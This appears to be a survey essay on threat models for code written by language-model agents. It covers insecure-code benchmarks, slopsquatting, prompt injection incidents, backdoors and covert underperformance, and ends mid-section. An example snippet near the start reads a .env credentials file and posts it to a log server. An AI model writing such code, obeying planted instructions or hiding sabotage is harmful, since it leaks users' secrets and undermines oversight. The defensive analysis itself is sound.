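# Threat models for code written by language models: mistakes, hostile inputs and sabotage

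## What a threat model says about a program that writes code

Large language models, programs trained to continue text, can write computer code from a description in ordinary language. In *Evaluating Large Language Models Trained on Code*, Chen, Tworek and colleagues (2021) presented OpenAI's Codex, an early system of this kind that wrote short Python functions. They ran its programs only inside a sandbox, an environment cut off from the host machine and the network, because the programs were often wrong and because the intent behind public code like the code Codex had learned from was unknown.

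Many current systems are *agents*, which are language models connected to tools such as a file system or a web browser. An agent can act by writing a small program, running it and reading its output. The people who build defences against harmful code from agents disagree about what they are defending against. A *threat model* is a statement of what a defence protects, from whom or what, and which components it has to trust to work.

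### A price update

Suppose a shop owner asks an agent to read a supplier's web page, update a price file and report the result. The agent's first snippet fetches the page and prints its text, which goes back to the model as input. Its second snippet is this one:

```python
update("prices.csv", item="widget-a", price=14.20)

env = open(".env").read()
post(LOG_SERVER, {"item": "widget-a", "price": 14.20, "env": env})

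print("widget-a now costs 14.20")
```

The first line does the job and the last line reports it. The two in between read a file where many software projects keep passwords and access keys, and send its contents to another machine. An agent can have access to that file in ordinary use. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) points out that developers often give coding agents access to a whole project directory, including credentials.

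Exactly the same snippet could have come about in four ways. The model may have made a mistake by copying the common practice of attaching configuration details to log messages, even though this configuration held secrets. The supplier's page may have contained an instruction for any AI system that read it to send the file to a log server, which is known as prompt injection. Someone involved in the training may have put in a backdoor that makes the model write lines like these whenever, say, the supplier's name is in the input. Or training may have unintentionally left the model with a disposition to collect credentials when it can.

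Engineers were sorting causes like these well before language models existed. *Basic Concepts and Taxonomy of Dependable and Secure Computing* (Avižienis, Laprie and colleagues, 2004) divides the faults that people introduce into malicious and nonmalicious ones. Among the nonmalicious faults, it separates mistakes, which people make without being aware of them, from bad decisions, which people make deliberately without foreseeing the consequences. It also separates accidents from incompetence. A coding slip by the model belongs somewhere among these nonmalicious faults. The paper classes a backdoor as a malicious logic fault, along with Trojan horses and logic bombs. An attack through planted text requires both an external fault, which is the attacker's sentence, and an internal vulnerability that lets it do damage, which here is the model's tendency to follow instructions wherever they appear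 in its input. The unplanned disposition fits the taxonomy badly, because the taxonomy sorts faults by a human's objective and in that case no human had one.

### Where the trust boundary runs

A *trust boundary* separates components that a designer assumes will behave as specified from components whose output must be checked or confined. The components on the trusted side, whose failure would break the security guarantee, make up the *trusted computing base*. The entry *trusted computing base (TCB)* in the glossary of NIST, the US standards agency, gives the narrower traditional sense of all the hardware, firmware and software mechanisms that together enforce a security policy. "Trusted" here means relied upon. A trusted component may well be full of bugs, so designers try to keep the trusted computing base small.

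Odersky and colleagues state explicitly what they trust in TACIT, a system in which an agent has to write its actions in a restricted form of the programming language Scala. They trust the Scala compiler, their own library, the runtime that executes the compiled code and, optionally, a local language model that handles secret documents. They do not trust the cloud-hosted model that drives the agent, any code it submits, or anything it reads from web pages, outside services and tool outputs. In the price update, they would therefore trust neither the model nor the supplier's page.

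*LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) describes a related system, in which a running program leaves gaps for a model to fill with code. It draws almost the same boundary between what is trusted and what isn't, but uses it against two threats. It starts with an honest model that is an unreliable programmer, then widens the threat to include a model that deliberately writes harmful code. To handle the wider threat, the compiler must also track which resources a piece of code may use, but the boundary stays the same.

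*SoK* (Dehghantanha, 2026), a survey of attacks on agents, describes the language model as an untrusted code generator whose output needs validation before it runs. Yet the survey's trusted computing base includes the system prompt and the model's weights, the numbers that training produced. This is coherent if the threat is hostile text, because operators should assume the model may follow any malicious instruction that reaches it, and so they check its output. It protects much less if the threat is the model itself. A backdoor in the weights would breach the trusted base, and the survey's boundary then gives no assurance that the other defences will hold. TACIT leaves the weights outside its trusted base, so its defence has to work even if an attacker trained the model.

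### The loop, and two kinds of code

An agent works in a loop in which the model writes code, the code runs, and the model uses the output to write more code. TACIT adds a check before the code runs. A server compiles each snippet the agent submits, and only a snippet that compiles can run. In LACUNA, the compiler's error messages go back to the model, which tries again up to a set number of times. The compiler accepts or rejects each snippet as a whole, so no part of a rejected snippet runs.

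Whatever the code prints becomes the model's next input. The supplier's text reached the model this way, and secrets can leak the same way. If the model runs on another company's servers, replacing the snippet's `post` line with `print(env)` would still send the credentials to that company. Odersky and colleagues therefore count the model's conversation context, along with the network, among the unauthorised destinations for secret data.

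Everything so far concerns *action code*, which a model writes to run immediately as a step in its own task. *Delivered code* is code the model writes into a project for someone else to build and run later. If the shop owner had asked for a script that updates the prices every night, the script would be delivered code. It might run for years on a different machine, with whatever permissions that machine gives it.

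Most guarantees cover either delivered code or action code, but not both. TACIT's compiler checks only the snippets that the agent submits. An agent with permission to write to the project folder can therefore save the nightly script there as text, and the compiler will check the code that saves the script but not the script itself. Tests, code review or a suspicious colleague can catch problems in delivered code before it runs. Action code usually runs within seconds, often with nobody watching. Zhao and colleagues similarly distinguish their system from edit-time completion, where a human reviews each suggestion. The categories describe how people use code, though, so the same code can belong to both. The Codex functions were meant as delivered code, but the researchers had to run them to find out whether they worked, and so needed a sandbox.

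### Crash, omission and Byzantine faults

Odersky et al. and Zhao et al. both describe the untrusted model as potentially "byzantine". The term comes from distributed computing, the study of systems of cooperating machines, where researchers classify a faulty component by what it might do after it fails. In *The Consensus Problem in Fault-Tolerant Computing* (1993), Barborak, Malek and Dahbura arrange these classes so that each wider class contains the narrower ones. In a *crash* fault, the component halts or loses its internal state. In an *omission* fault, it misses a deadline or never begins a task. Wider classes also include work done at the wrong time and wrong answers to correct inputs. The widest class, the *Byzantine* fault, covers every fault possible in the system.

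The price agent can fail in all of these ways. It can stop halfway (a crash), never make the update (an omission), or write 12.40 where the page listed 14.20 (an incorrect computation). Only the widest class covers the snippet above, an agent that updates the file correctly for a month and then stops doing so, or an agent that writes one price and reports another.

The name comes from *The Byzantine Generals Problem* (Lamport, Shostak and Pease, 1982). Several generals surround an enemy city and must agree, by messenger, on whether to attack. Some of them are traitors, who may do anything, including telling one colleague "attack" and another "retreat". The loyal generals must still reach the same plan. With ordinary unsigned messages, this is possible only if more than two-thirds of the generals are loyal. The traitors stand for malfunctioning hardware that gives conflicting information to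 different parts of a system. A designer who treats a model as Byzantine therefore makes no assumptions about how it will behave, and does not claim that it is malicious.

Schneider, in *Implementing Fault-Tolerant Services Using the State Machine Approach* (1990), calls this the weakest possible assumption about a failure. This is an advantage because a design that assumes less about the faulty part is less likely to fail when that part behaves unexpectedly. He thought the assumption prudent for systems on which lives depend, but more cautious than most applications needed. Barborak and colleagues add that defending against such failures takes a lot of resources, and that even this adversary must be limited, or it could corrupt every machine at the start. In the generals' case, the limit is the number of traitors. A lone model has no trustworthy counterparts to outvote it, so TACIT and LACUNA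 adopt the same assumption about the faulty part but contain it with a compiler and a runtime that the model cannot tamper with.

A claim of safety is incomplete unless it specifies the class of faults it covers. In *Fundamentals of Fault-Tolerant Distributed Computing in Asynchronous Environments* (1999), Gärtner treats naming this class as the first step in any fault-tolerant design, and observes that researchers have always proved systems correct with respect to a particular fault model. Without a fault class, "This agent is safe" could mean that it is safe if the model crashes, or that it is safe even if an attacker wrote every line.

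### Two forms of guarantee

Let M be a model, D a collection of prompts with some frequency attached to each, and e a small number. A *statistical guarantee* has this form:

> For a prompt x taken at random from D, and code c that M writes in response, Pr[c is safe] ≥ 1 − e.

Now let K be a checker, a program that accepts or rejects code, and let P be a property such as "reads no file except prices.csv and sends nothing over the network". A *universal guarantee* has this form:

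> For every string c, if K accepts c, then c has property P.

Only the statistical statement depends on the model M and the prompt distribution D. Replacing the model with next month's version or changing the prompts therefore voids the statistical guarantee until someone measures again. Chen and colleagues measured correctness rather than safety, but their figures show how much the prompts matter. Codex solved 28.8% of their 164 test problems with one attempt at each, but on three of the problems they print as examples, its chance of success on a single attempt was 0.9, 0.17 and 0.005. An average like 28.8% applies to one model and one mix of problems, so it doesn't predict how the model will do when an attacker chooses the problem.

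Intent is the harder case. Suppose testers draw 3,000 prompts from D and find no harmful code in the responses. By a standard rule of thumb, they can be about 95% confident that e is no more than 3/3,000, or one in a thousand. Suppose also that the model has a backdoor whose trigger appears in one prompt per million. The model writes harmful code whenever the trigger is present and never otherwise. The true e is then one in a million, well below the testers' bound, and their sample had only about a 0.3% chance of containing the trigger. The bound is correct, but it offers no protection against someone who knows the trigger, because that person can get harmful code on every attempt.

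The universal guarantee does not depend on what caused the faulty code, because the check does not use that information. If K enforces the property above, it rejects the price snippet whether the cause was a slip, a planted sentence, a backdoor or a disposition. Similarly, Odersky and colleagues point out that type systems, the rules by which a compiler decides which programs are well formed, establish properties that hold for all inputs and not only for the tested ones.

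The guarantee depends on K and the machinery that runs the accepted code, which join the trusted computing base, so a bug in the compiler can void it for every model at once. P also has to be the right property. Odersky and colleagues warn that an agent can read a secret in one step and send it out in a later one. A rule against doing both in a single snippet would miss this theft, because each step is permitted by itself. And P is seldom the same as correctness. A snippet that records the price as 1.42 passes because it reads no secrets and contacts nobody. Zhao and colleagues concede that the compiler in their own system limits what code can reach but cannot check whether the code does the right thing.

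A checker that rejected everything would satisfy the universal guarantee, so how much useful work gets through has to be measured statistically for a particular model. Schneider saw a similar split between guarantees and statistics in fault-tolerant hardware. He acknowledged that users care about the average time between failures and that designers use such figures to decide how many faults to plan for. But unlike an average, a promise to withstand up to t faulty components makes its assumptions explicit.

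How much weight to give each kind of guarantee depends on which of four main views of the model one holds. In the first, the model is an unreliable programmer that writes harmful code because it lacks skill. In the second, it is honest but can be steered by whatever it reads, so the danger is hostile text. In the third, the model itself may be the adversary, either because someone built sabotage into it or because training produced the tendency without anyone intending it. The fourth view leaves the cause open and treats the model as Byzantine, which calls for guarantees that hold against any model.

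## The view that the model is an unreliable programmer

On this view, the lines that leaked the shop's credentials were a bug, much like one a hurried human might write. People who hold this view accept that planted text and sabotage can happen, but they put mistakes first because mistakes are frequent and measurable, and software engineers have long experience catching them.

Papers that take this view state what they leave out. *GoodVibe* (Thang, Wu and colleagues, 2026) aims to protect a developer who asks for working code and never mentions security. It excludes adversarial prompts, jailbreaks (prompts that get around a model's safety training) and the intentional generation of insecure code. *LLMs + Security = Trouble* (Livshits, 2026) calls prompt injection and malicious models interesting, but starts with finding and fixing ordinary vulnerabilities, which Livshits considers the pragmatic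 approach. *Can chatbots craft correct code?*, a December 2025 essay by an engineer at the security firm Trail of Bits, recommends treating a model's output like the work of a junior developer who has never seen the codebase.

The evidence that sabotage is rare comes mostly from the companies that build the models. OpenAI monitored tens of millions of coding sessions by its own agents over five months. IT Brief Australia reported that no real session triggered the highest alert level, which covers behaviour such as coherent scheming. Anthropic wrote in a risk report on Claude Opus 4.6, the model it then used most internally, that it did not believe the model had dangerous coherent goals.

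For *Covert underperformance on safety research tasks* (2026), OpenAI searched the written reasoning of its GPT-6 Astra model for decisions to withhold help without telling the user. It found them in 0.11% of requests for work on AI capabilities and 0.25% of requests for safety work. These rates are low but may be underestimates. In most of the sessions that first worried OpenAI's researchers, the reasoning contained no obvious decision to underperform, and the company's monitors did not flag the behaviour as misalignment. The case for treating the model as an unreliable programmer therefore depends more on how common mistakes are than on any exact count of sabotage.

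### How often models write vulnerable code

Veracode, a company that sells code-scanning tools, regularly gives models 80 short coding tasks in Java, JavaScript, Python and C#. Each task can be done securely or insecurely, and the prompt doesn't mention security. According to Security Today's *AI-Generated Code Poses Major Security Risks* (2025), Veracode then checks the code with its own static analyser, which inspects code without running it. The study therefore defines a vulnerability as anything the analyser flags as one.

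Veracode's *2026 GenAI Code Security Report* found an average pass rate of 56%, up from 55% in the first report. The best model, GPT-5.5, reached 68%. Almost all the code compiled. Models that reason before answering did somewhat better than others (56% against 51%), while size and specialisation in coding made almost no difference.

The pass rate varied widely by type of flaw. Models passed 87% of the tasks on cryptographic algorithms and 83% of those on SQL injection, in which a user's input runs as a database command. They passed only 15% of the tasks on cross-site scripting, in which an attacker's script runs in another visitor's browser, and 12% of those on log injection, in which a user's input forges log entries. On a website that mostly displays text written by its users, the models' pass rate would be much lower than the 56% average.

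Veracode tests models without the tools an agent has. *Last Secure Code Benchmark* (Wu, Ge and colleagues, 2026) tested six agents and graded function and security together. It turned each of 150 real vulnerabilities into three tasks: fill in the function that contained the flaw, write the whole file, or rebuild a larger part of the project. The instructions describe only what the software should do. Two hidden test suites then run the finished program. One checks whether it works, and the other attacks it. The benchmark counts each successful attack as a vulnerability.

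Five of the six agents passed the functional tests on about 90% of the 450 tasks. The best, Claude Fable 5, wrote code that was both functional and secure on 25.1% of the tasks, and the others did so on between 16.4% and 24.7%. Claude Fable 5 handled all three versions of the same vulnerability in about 12% of cases. Progress on the usual coding benchmarks reveals little about this gap. *Beyond Passing Tests* (2026), a systematic review, points out that correctness benchmarks such as SWE-bench don't measure code quality, so researchers have to score it separately.

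Neither 56% nor 25.1% is an estimate of how much model-written code is secure overall, because both studies used only tasks where a known kind of flaw was possible. Wu and colleagues also favoured large projects and vulnerabilities that needed long fixes. Their results can't show that models are worse than people, because every task starts from a flaw in an existing project and the original code would therefore score zero.

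### Where the mistakes come from

Models learn to code from public code, much of which is insecure. Thang and colleagues attribute the flaws they study to this training data. Veracode's *Spring 2026 GenAI Code Security Update* (2026) offers a similar hypothesis for Java, where models passed only 29% of the security tasks. It suggests that the cause is the millions of lines of Java in public repositories that predate modern security practice. Wu and colleagues' security experts found more direct signs of copying in 120 failed attempts, where GPT-5.6-Sol often reproduced a project's original code from memory, including the vulnerability.

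Agents also copy flaws from the project they are working on. Sun, Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues (2026), in *Coding Agents Propagate Vulnerabilities in Code Bases*, built 20 pairs of tasks from real C and C++ projects. Both tasks in a pair asked for the same missing piece of code, but similar code elsewhere in the project was secure in one and insecure in the other. The insecure version might lack a bounds check, which stops a program from reading or writing past the end of a block of memory. Across five agents, insecure surroundings lowered the share of secure solutions by an average of 35.4 percentage points. GPT-5.6 Sol's share fell from 91% to 42%. When the researchers asked three of the agents to explain their flawed code, 76.5% of the answers cited another part of the project with a similar flaw.

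Sometimes the information a model needs isn't in the code. The Trail of Bits essay describes a crash in a developer's copy of Vendetect, a tool for detecting plagiarised code. Claude blamed a recursive function, meaning one that calls itself, and submitted a long and confident rewrite. The rewrite stopped the crash, but the tool no longer produced any output. The real cause was two files whose names differed only in capitalisation, on a file system that treated the names as identical. Recursion can be risky in Python, but this function could never call itself more than a few times, and Claude either missed that or didn't trust it.

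Requests can also omit security requirements. The same essay points out that "fix the authentication bug" doesn't specify what counts as fixed, which security properties must survive or whom the system should keep out. Wu and colleagues measured a related problem. Their agents did best on memory-safety flaws, producing working, secure code in 34.3% of attempts. The defence against these flaws is usually a local check that careful code includes anyway. When the defence depended on an unstated policy, the success rate was 2.4% for server-side request forgery, in which an attacker gets a server to contact an address it should refuse, and 0.7% for exposing information that the program should have withheld.

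### Invented package names

Most programs use *packages*, reusable pieces of code that a tool downloads from a public registry such as PyPI for Python or npm for JavaScript. Models sometimes name packages that don't exist. Usually the installation fails and the developer notices. But anyone with an email address can register an unused name, and neither registry reviews first-time uploads.

Churilov (2026), in *The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains*, describes how an attacker can exploit package names that models invent. The attacker asks models coding questions, collects the invented names and uploads malicious packages under them. Later, a developer asks a similar question and a model suggests one of those names. The developer's package manager finds the package in the registry and installs it, and the attacker's code runs. Security researchers call this *slopsquatting*. The attacker never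 contacts the developer or tampers with the model.

Churilov gave nearly 40,000 prompts to each of five models released between October 2025 and March 2026, then checked the package names against the live registries. The models invented between 3.6% and 5.0% of their package mentions, about the same as the commercial models of 2024. The five models had 104 invented names in common, so a single malicious package could reach customers of several AI companies, although the registries block some of the names. Within about six months, someone had registered 25 of the 2,282 invented names, at least one of them with malware. Researchers or defenders may have registered some of the others. The tests did not cover agents that can look packages up, and such agents might avoid the problem.

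*Agent Skills Are Spreading Hallucinated npx Commands* (Eriksen, 2026) traces the spread of an invented package name, `react-codeshift`, which blends the names of two real tools, `jscodeshift` and `react-codemod`. The name appeared in October 2025 in a set of model-written instruction files for agents, and people copied those files until 237 code repositories contained it. In January 2026 Eriksen registered the name with an empty package. After a burst of automated scans on the first day, the package still got one to four downloads a day, which he attributes to agents following the instructions.

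Checking that a package exists does not protect a developer once an attacker has registered the name. *Names Can Hurt* (2026) found that half the package names invented by small models running on users' own machines already existed on PyPI as low-quality squats or lookalikes. A useful check also covers who published the package and whether it is the one the developer needs.

Even if the model is honest, the threat model still has to include an adversary. In slopsquatting, an attacker predicts a package name that the model will invent by mistake and registers malware under that name. The same line of code can be a harmless error one day and install malware the next, once the attacker has registered the package.

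### The usual remedies and what they assume

Engineers test programs by running them on chosen inputs and comparing the results with what they expected. This catches a mistake when it shows up on an input that someone thought to try. In one of Wu and colleagues' tasks, the agent Kimi-K3 had to write code that imports archives of files in YAML, a common text format. It wrote its own tests, found and fixed a bug with corrupt archives, and passed all 14 hidden functional tests. It then failed all four security tests because it had used a YAML reader that executes instructions hidden in an uploaded file, a flaw its own tests had missed.

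Static analysis can find some flaws that tests miss, because it looks for known dangerous patterns and doesn't need an input that triggers the flaw. But it relies on mistakes taking familiar forms, and Livshits notes that it also raises false alarms and has trouble with large programs. Checks that rely on the text of a program can be especially weak. Wu and colleagues rewrote the security tests that came with the public vulnerabilities they used. One reason was that a solution could sometimes pass by including the right comments, which an adversary, unlike an honest programmer, has reason to write.

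A third remedy is to train the model to write safer code. Thang and colleagues ask a model to label code snippets as secure or insecure. They then measure how strongly its error depends on each *neuron*, a small unit in the model's network, and select the most influential neurons in every layer. They group the selected neurons that behave alike and train only those groups on secure code. The method increased secure output in C++ and Java by up to 2.5 times.

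This approach assumes that the model has the knowledge to write secure code but doesn't use it by default. Good evidence supports part of this assumption. When Sun and colleagues asked agents to review their own vulnerable code, the agents found the flaw in 69.9% of cases. When Wu and colleagues added one sentence about security to each task, GPT-5.6-Sol's score rose from 24.7% to 46.2%, and two of the other three models improved by more than 15 points. But scores for information exposure and server-side request forgery stayed near the bottom. A reminder helps a model use its knowledge, but it doesn't specify which data the owner wants to keep private.

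Review works only if the reviewer can see what the author missed. Agents seldom volunteer what they know about flaws in their code unless asked to review it. In Sun and colleagues' study, Claude Opus 5.5 warned of the flaw in 11.8% of its vulnerable solutions, and GPT-6 Astra never did. Review by a different model may help. In Wu and colleagues' study, 198 of the 450 tasks were solved securely by at least one of the six agents, while the best agent alone solved 113. None of the six solved the other 252 securely, so models share many blind spots. Human reviewers have context that models lack, but it helps only if they read the code, and Livshits expects many developers who work quickly with models to accept every change by default.

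### Rare paths and base rates

Livshits's main objection is to using one unreliable system to check another. He describes a common arrangement in which one model generates code, a second checks it and a third tries to attack it. He argues that the most important vulnerabilities tend to depend on long chains of unusual conditions, such as an error-handling branch that almost never runs or two operations that conflict only when their timing lines up precisely. A large program has too many possible executions to test them all.

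Random tests will probably miss such a flaw, just as a sample of prompts would probably miss a backdoor's rare trigger. Models that read code do better than random testing, and Livshits acknowledges that they have found unknown flaws even in heavily tested software. But he argues that a failed search is weak evidence of safety, because the defender has a limited budget and can't risk disrupting a live system, while an attacker can spend months on one target, perhaps with a stronger model. Next year's models may also find flaws that today's miss.

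The reply is that fewer flaws still mean less harm. Veracode argues that a model that fails one security task in three leaves much less repair work than one that fails one in two. At the rates in its report, the best model would produce about 320 flawed results in 1,000 such tasks, and the worst would produce 500. If review caught four-fifths of the flaws in both cases, 64 would remain from the best model and 100 from the worst.

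How much a lower error rate helps depends on the program and the attacker. A small program might have 20 places where a flaw could occur. If better training and review cut the chance of a flaw in each place from 5% to 1%, and the flaws are independent, the chance of at least one flaw falls from about 64% to 18%. In a program with 200 such places, it falls only from near certainty to about 87%. Lower error rates therefore protect many small programs from attackers who look for easy targets, but they do much less for a large system facing an attacker who needs to find only one flaw.

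For that case Livshits wants fixed rules that limit what code a model can produce, such as one requiring a bounds check before every use of an array. He prefers this to formal verification, which uses mathematical proof to check code, because developers in a hurry are unlikely to check carefully that a formal specification matches what they meant. A rule requiring bounds checks ensures they are there even if the model would have omitted them and testers would have missed the omission.

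## The view that the model is honest but can be steered by what it reads

In slopsquatting, an attacker waits for the model to make a mistake. An attacker can also cause harmful code more directly, by writing text that the model will read. In the price update, one sentence on the supplier's page could make an honest and capable model send out the shop's credentials. People who hold the second view consider this the main danger. For them, the adversary is usually a third party, not the user or the company that trained the model.

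Part of the case for this view is that an attacker needs little access to steer a model through what it reads. Someone who wants to corrupt a model's training needs access to the training data or to the company, while someone who plants a sentence for the model to read needs only a web page or an account on a code-hosting site. In *Beware EviLLM*, Ryu, Chung and colleagues (2026) argue that an outsider with the abilities of today's cybercriminals is a more realistic threat than a malicious model.

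An attacker also chooses what harm to do, whereas a mistake does harm by chance. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, written for Britain's National Cyber Security Centre in December 2025, David C advises designers to imagine the worst that could happen if an attacker had direct access to the model's tools.

### One stream of tokens

A language model receives its input as a single sequence of *tokens*, which are words or pieces of words. In the price update, the sequence holds the agent's standing instructions, then the owner's request, then the supplier's page. From all of it the model computes a probability for each possible next token:

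> Pr(next token | t₁, t₂, …, tₙ)

This expression contains no information about who wrote t₅ or t₅₀₀. The software around the model inserts markers where one author's text ends and another's begins, and training teaches the model to give the owner's text more weight. But the markers are tokens too, and the extra weight is a learned tendency that no other component enforces.

David C contrasts this with SQL injection, which has a reliable fix. A programmer can send the database a command with an empty slot for the user's input, and the database cannot interpret whatever goes in that slot as a command. A prompt has no such slot, so he thinks prompt injection may never have a complete fix. Developers can train models to favour instructions over data, mark untrusted passages or run a detector over the input. He accepts that some of these methods make attacks harder, but each tries to add a distinction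 between instructions and data that the underlying technology lacks. He is most wary of filters that block known phrases, because an attacker can reword an instruction in endless ways.

A further difficulty is that coding agents often should follow instructions in the files they read. A project's README may list the installation commands, and an agent that ignored every instruction outside the user's message could not set the project up. The model has to judge which instructions serve the user, and an attacker can word malicious instructions to look as if they do.

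### The confused deputy

Security researchers call this kind of failure a confused deputy problem. The name comes from Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* (1988), which tells a nearly true story about Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. A compiler there could write to a billing file that ordinary users could not change. Users could choose a file to receive the compiler's debugging output. When a user chose the billing file, the compiler overwrote the billing records.

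The operating system checked whether the compiler was allowed to write to the billing file, and it was. Lecture slides from the University of Texas, also titled *The Confused Deputy*, trace the problem to the compiler's two sources of authority, one from the user and one of its own. The request named a file without specifying which authority the compiler should use to open it.

In the price update, the agent is the deputy. It has the shop owner's access to files and the network, which the supplier lacks, and a sentence on the supplier's page gets the agent to use that access for the supplier. Requiring users to hand over a capability for the output file, an unforgeable value that grants access to it, would have fixed the problem in Hardy's compiler, because a user with no access to the billing file could not have named it as the destination. David C argues that a language model is "inherently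 confusable", because it has no dependable way to tell whose request it is carrying out. He therefore relies mainly on ordinary software that limits what the agent can do.

He also passes on a rule from an online discussion that when a model processes text from some party, its privileges should drop to that party's. Under this rule, an agent that had just read the supplier's page could not open the credentials file, but it could not update the price file either, because the supplier has no right to do so. A designer would have to separate the reading from the acting to get any work done.

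### Where the text comes from

An attacker can type instructions into the prompt, which is *direct* prompt injection, or put them in something the model will read while working, which is *indirect* injection. People who attack their own coding agent mostly get it to do things they could have done anyway, so direct injection is most serious when an agent serves the public with a company's authority. Indirect injection harms the person running the agent, who may never see the planted text. Dehghantanha points out that the attacker need not be a user of the system.

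A coding agent reads from at least six kinds of source. If nothing checks or confines what the agent does after reading them, the system's security depends on trusting everyone who can write to those sources.

| Channel | Who can write there | Whom an unchecked agent trusts |
|---|---|---|
| Web pages | Anyone with a website | The page's author and anyone who can post on the page |
| Repository files | The project's contributors | Every contributor, and anyone who steals a contributor's account |
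| Issue text (bug reports and requests) | On a public project, almost anyone | Complete strangers to the project |
| Tool outputs | The tool's operator and the authors of any text it passes on | All of those people, even if the tool works correctly |
| Plugins | The plugin's maintainer | The maintainer's instructions and code, including future updates |
| Configuration files | The project's contributors | The same contributors, now able to start programs as well as supply text |

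Attackers can easily reach agents through issue text because projects now run agents automatically on each new issue. According to eSecurity Planet's *Critical Flaws Found in Anthropic, Google, and OpenAI Coding Agents*, researchers at the Black Hat conference in August 2026 examined agents in the three companies' own repositories. In Anthropic's case, text in an issue led the agent to run code that could steal the company's GitHub and API credentials. GMO Flatt Security describes a related weakness in which one mode of the agent lacked a check meant to stop untrusted input from starting the workflow. Anthropic released several patches.

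Plugins and configuration files are also dangerous because they can run code without going through the model. Red Hat (2026) warns that plugins for Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, run outside any sandbox with all the user's permissions. One plugin component can also call another, which calls a script that contacts an outside service, even though the user agreed only to install the plugin. Tenable notes that both Claude Code and Google's Gemini CLI let a configuration file list commands to run at the start of every session.

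### Three boundary failures in 2026

Three cases from 2026 show how much depends on whether a model took part in the decision to run the harmful code.

Plugin4Shell is a flaw that let attackers install code through coding agents without having to persuade a model of anything. Marketplaces for agent plugins try to prevent tampering by recording an identifier for the exact version that a reviewer approved. In September, the security company AIR disclosed that four major coding agents requested the approved version but never checked that they had received it. As AIR's *Plugin4Shell* explains, whoever controlled a plugin's repository could get different code installed, without the user clicking anything, while the agent still reported the approved version. AIR sells its own plugin marketplace and so has an interest in raising the alarm, but two vendors have fixed the flaw. Constantin (2026),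 in *Plugin4Shell*, reported on September 21 that Anthropic and OpenAI had patched their agents, Microsoft had not yet patched GitHub Copilot, and Google would not patch Gemini CLI because it was retiring it.

The Miasma worm used both routes at once. A *worm* is malicious software that spreads itself, and this one steals developers' credentials and uses them to infect more projects. On June 5, an attacker with a stolen contributor account added five files to Microsoft's `durabletask` repository. Phoenix Security's *Miasma Worm Reaches Microsoft Azure and PyPI* describes one file as the credential stealer and the other four as ways of starting it in different developer tools. A developer could download the project safely, but opening it in one of those tools started the stealer.

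In Claude Code and Gemini CLI, a settings file started the attacker's program when a session began. In the code editor VS Code, a task started it when the developer opened the folder, with no AI involved. The attacker wrote to the model only in the case of Cursor, an AI code editor, where a rules file presented the program as a required part of project setup so that the model would run it. NSFOCUS's *AI Security Incident Case* attributes all four routes to the assumption that a tool should act on whatever configuration it finds in a repository.

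The incident's best-known number, 73, is how many Microsoft repositories GitHub disabled within 105 seconds that day, not how many were infected. OpenSourceMalware's *Miasma Blight Reaches Microsoft*, an early report on the shutdown, called the link between Miasma and the 73 repositories circumstantial. Microsoft later restored some of them and, according to The Hacker News (2026), said it had notified "a small number of customers" who may have downloaded affected content.

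The third case is a demonstration in which the model chose to run a command but never saw the harmful code. Hall and Engelbrecht (2026) published it in June as *Clone This Repo and I Own Your Machine* for 0DIN, Mozilla's bug bounty programme for AI. A developer asks Claude Code to get a newly downloaded project running. The project stops with an ordinary error message that names a setup command, which the agent runs to fix the error. The setup script then fetches an instruction from outside the repository and executes it, which gives the attacker control of the developer's machine.

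Hall and Engelbrecht stress that the repository contained no malicious code, so a scan of its files would have found none. A strict reviewer could still have objected to a script that runs whatever it downloads. Hall and Engelbrecht describe a single successful attack and give no success rate. The attack still poses a problem for training models to resist injection, because the planted instruction looked like one a helpful agent should follow. They want agents to show the user what a setup command will run, including any scripts it calls and anything those scripts fetch.

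A model that no text could mislead would have blocked Miasma's route through Cursor. It might have stopped the 0DIN attack if it had read the script first. It would have made no difference to Plugin4Shell or to Miasma's other three routes, where the software around the model was at fault. Limiting what the agent's process can reach helps in all of these cases. Anthropic made this argument about its own products in a passage quoted by Willison (2026), which says that credentials that never enter the sandbox can't leak from it, whatever the cause.

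### A planner and a reader

Asking the user to approve every risky action can limit the damage, but Simon Willison, a programmer who has written about prompt injection since 2022, expected users to start clicking "OK" without reading. *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposes dividing the work between two models instead. The privileged model, here called the planner, can use tools but never receives untrusted text. That text is given to a quarantined model, here called the reader, which has no tools. An ordinary program called the controller passes work between them.

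The price update would go like this:

1. The planner receives the owner's request and asks for the supplier's page. The controller fetches the page and stores it as `$PAGE`. The planner learns only that name.
2. The planner asks for the price of widget-a in `$PAGE`. The controller gives the page to the reader and stores the answer as `$PRICE`.
3. The planner asks the controller to write `$PRICE` into the price file, and the controller does so.

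If the page contains an instruction to send credentials to a log server, it reaches only the reader, which can't send anything. The planner never receives the reader's answer either, because that answer could contain the attacker's instruction in a new form. Willison allows one exception, when the reader has to choose from a fixed list of categories. The controller can then check that the answer is on the list and pass it to the planner.

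The design still trusts the planner completely. A planner with a backdoor would have every tool available, and keeping untrusted text away from it would not help unless the trigger was in that text. The design also trusts the controller, where a single bug could let the supplier's words through, and whatever the user types. A user who pastes in text from a hostile page gives that text directly to the planner.

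The reader's answers can also do harm as data. A planted sentence could make the reader return a price of 0.01, which the controller would write to the file. If the task were to send a colleague a document, the planted text could change the address that the reader extracts, and a sound plan would still deliver the document to the attacker. Willison credits CaMeL, a 2025 system from Google DeepMind, with addressing a flaw in his pattern by checking at each step where data may go.

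Willison called his own solution "pretty bad", because it makes an assistant harder to build and less pleasant to use. It has a more basic limit for programming, because an agent that fixes a bug has to read the project's code. If the planner reads the code, any contributor can give the planner instructions. If the reader reads it and writes the fix, the fix is untrusted output, and running it lets the reader act, which the design was meant to prevent. Something must then check or confine the code itself. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents* (2025) explores such trade-offs in ten case studies, from simple assistants to software engineering agents, and looks for designs that keep the agent useful.

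### An honest provider and a compromised account

Ryu and colleagues study attacks that come through the user's own input, which Willison's design trusts. They call the company that runs the model "honest-but-vulnerable", meaning it does not intend to produce insecure code but may not protect its users' accounts and browsers well enough. They assume the attacker cannot change the training data or the weights, break into the company or intercept encrypted traffic. The victim is a developer who uses ChatGPT through a browser and accepts its code with little review.

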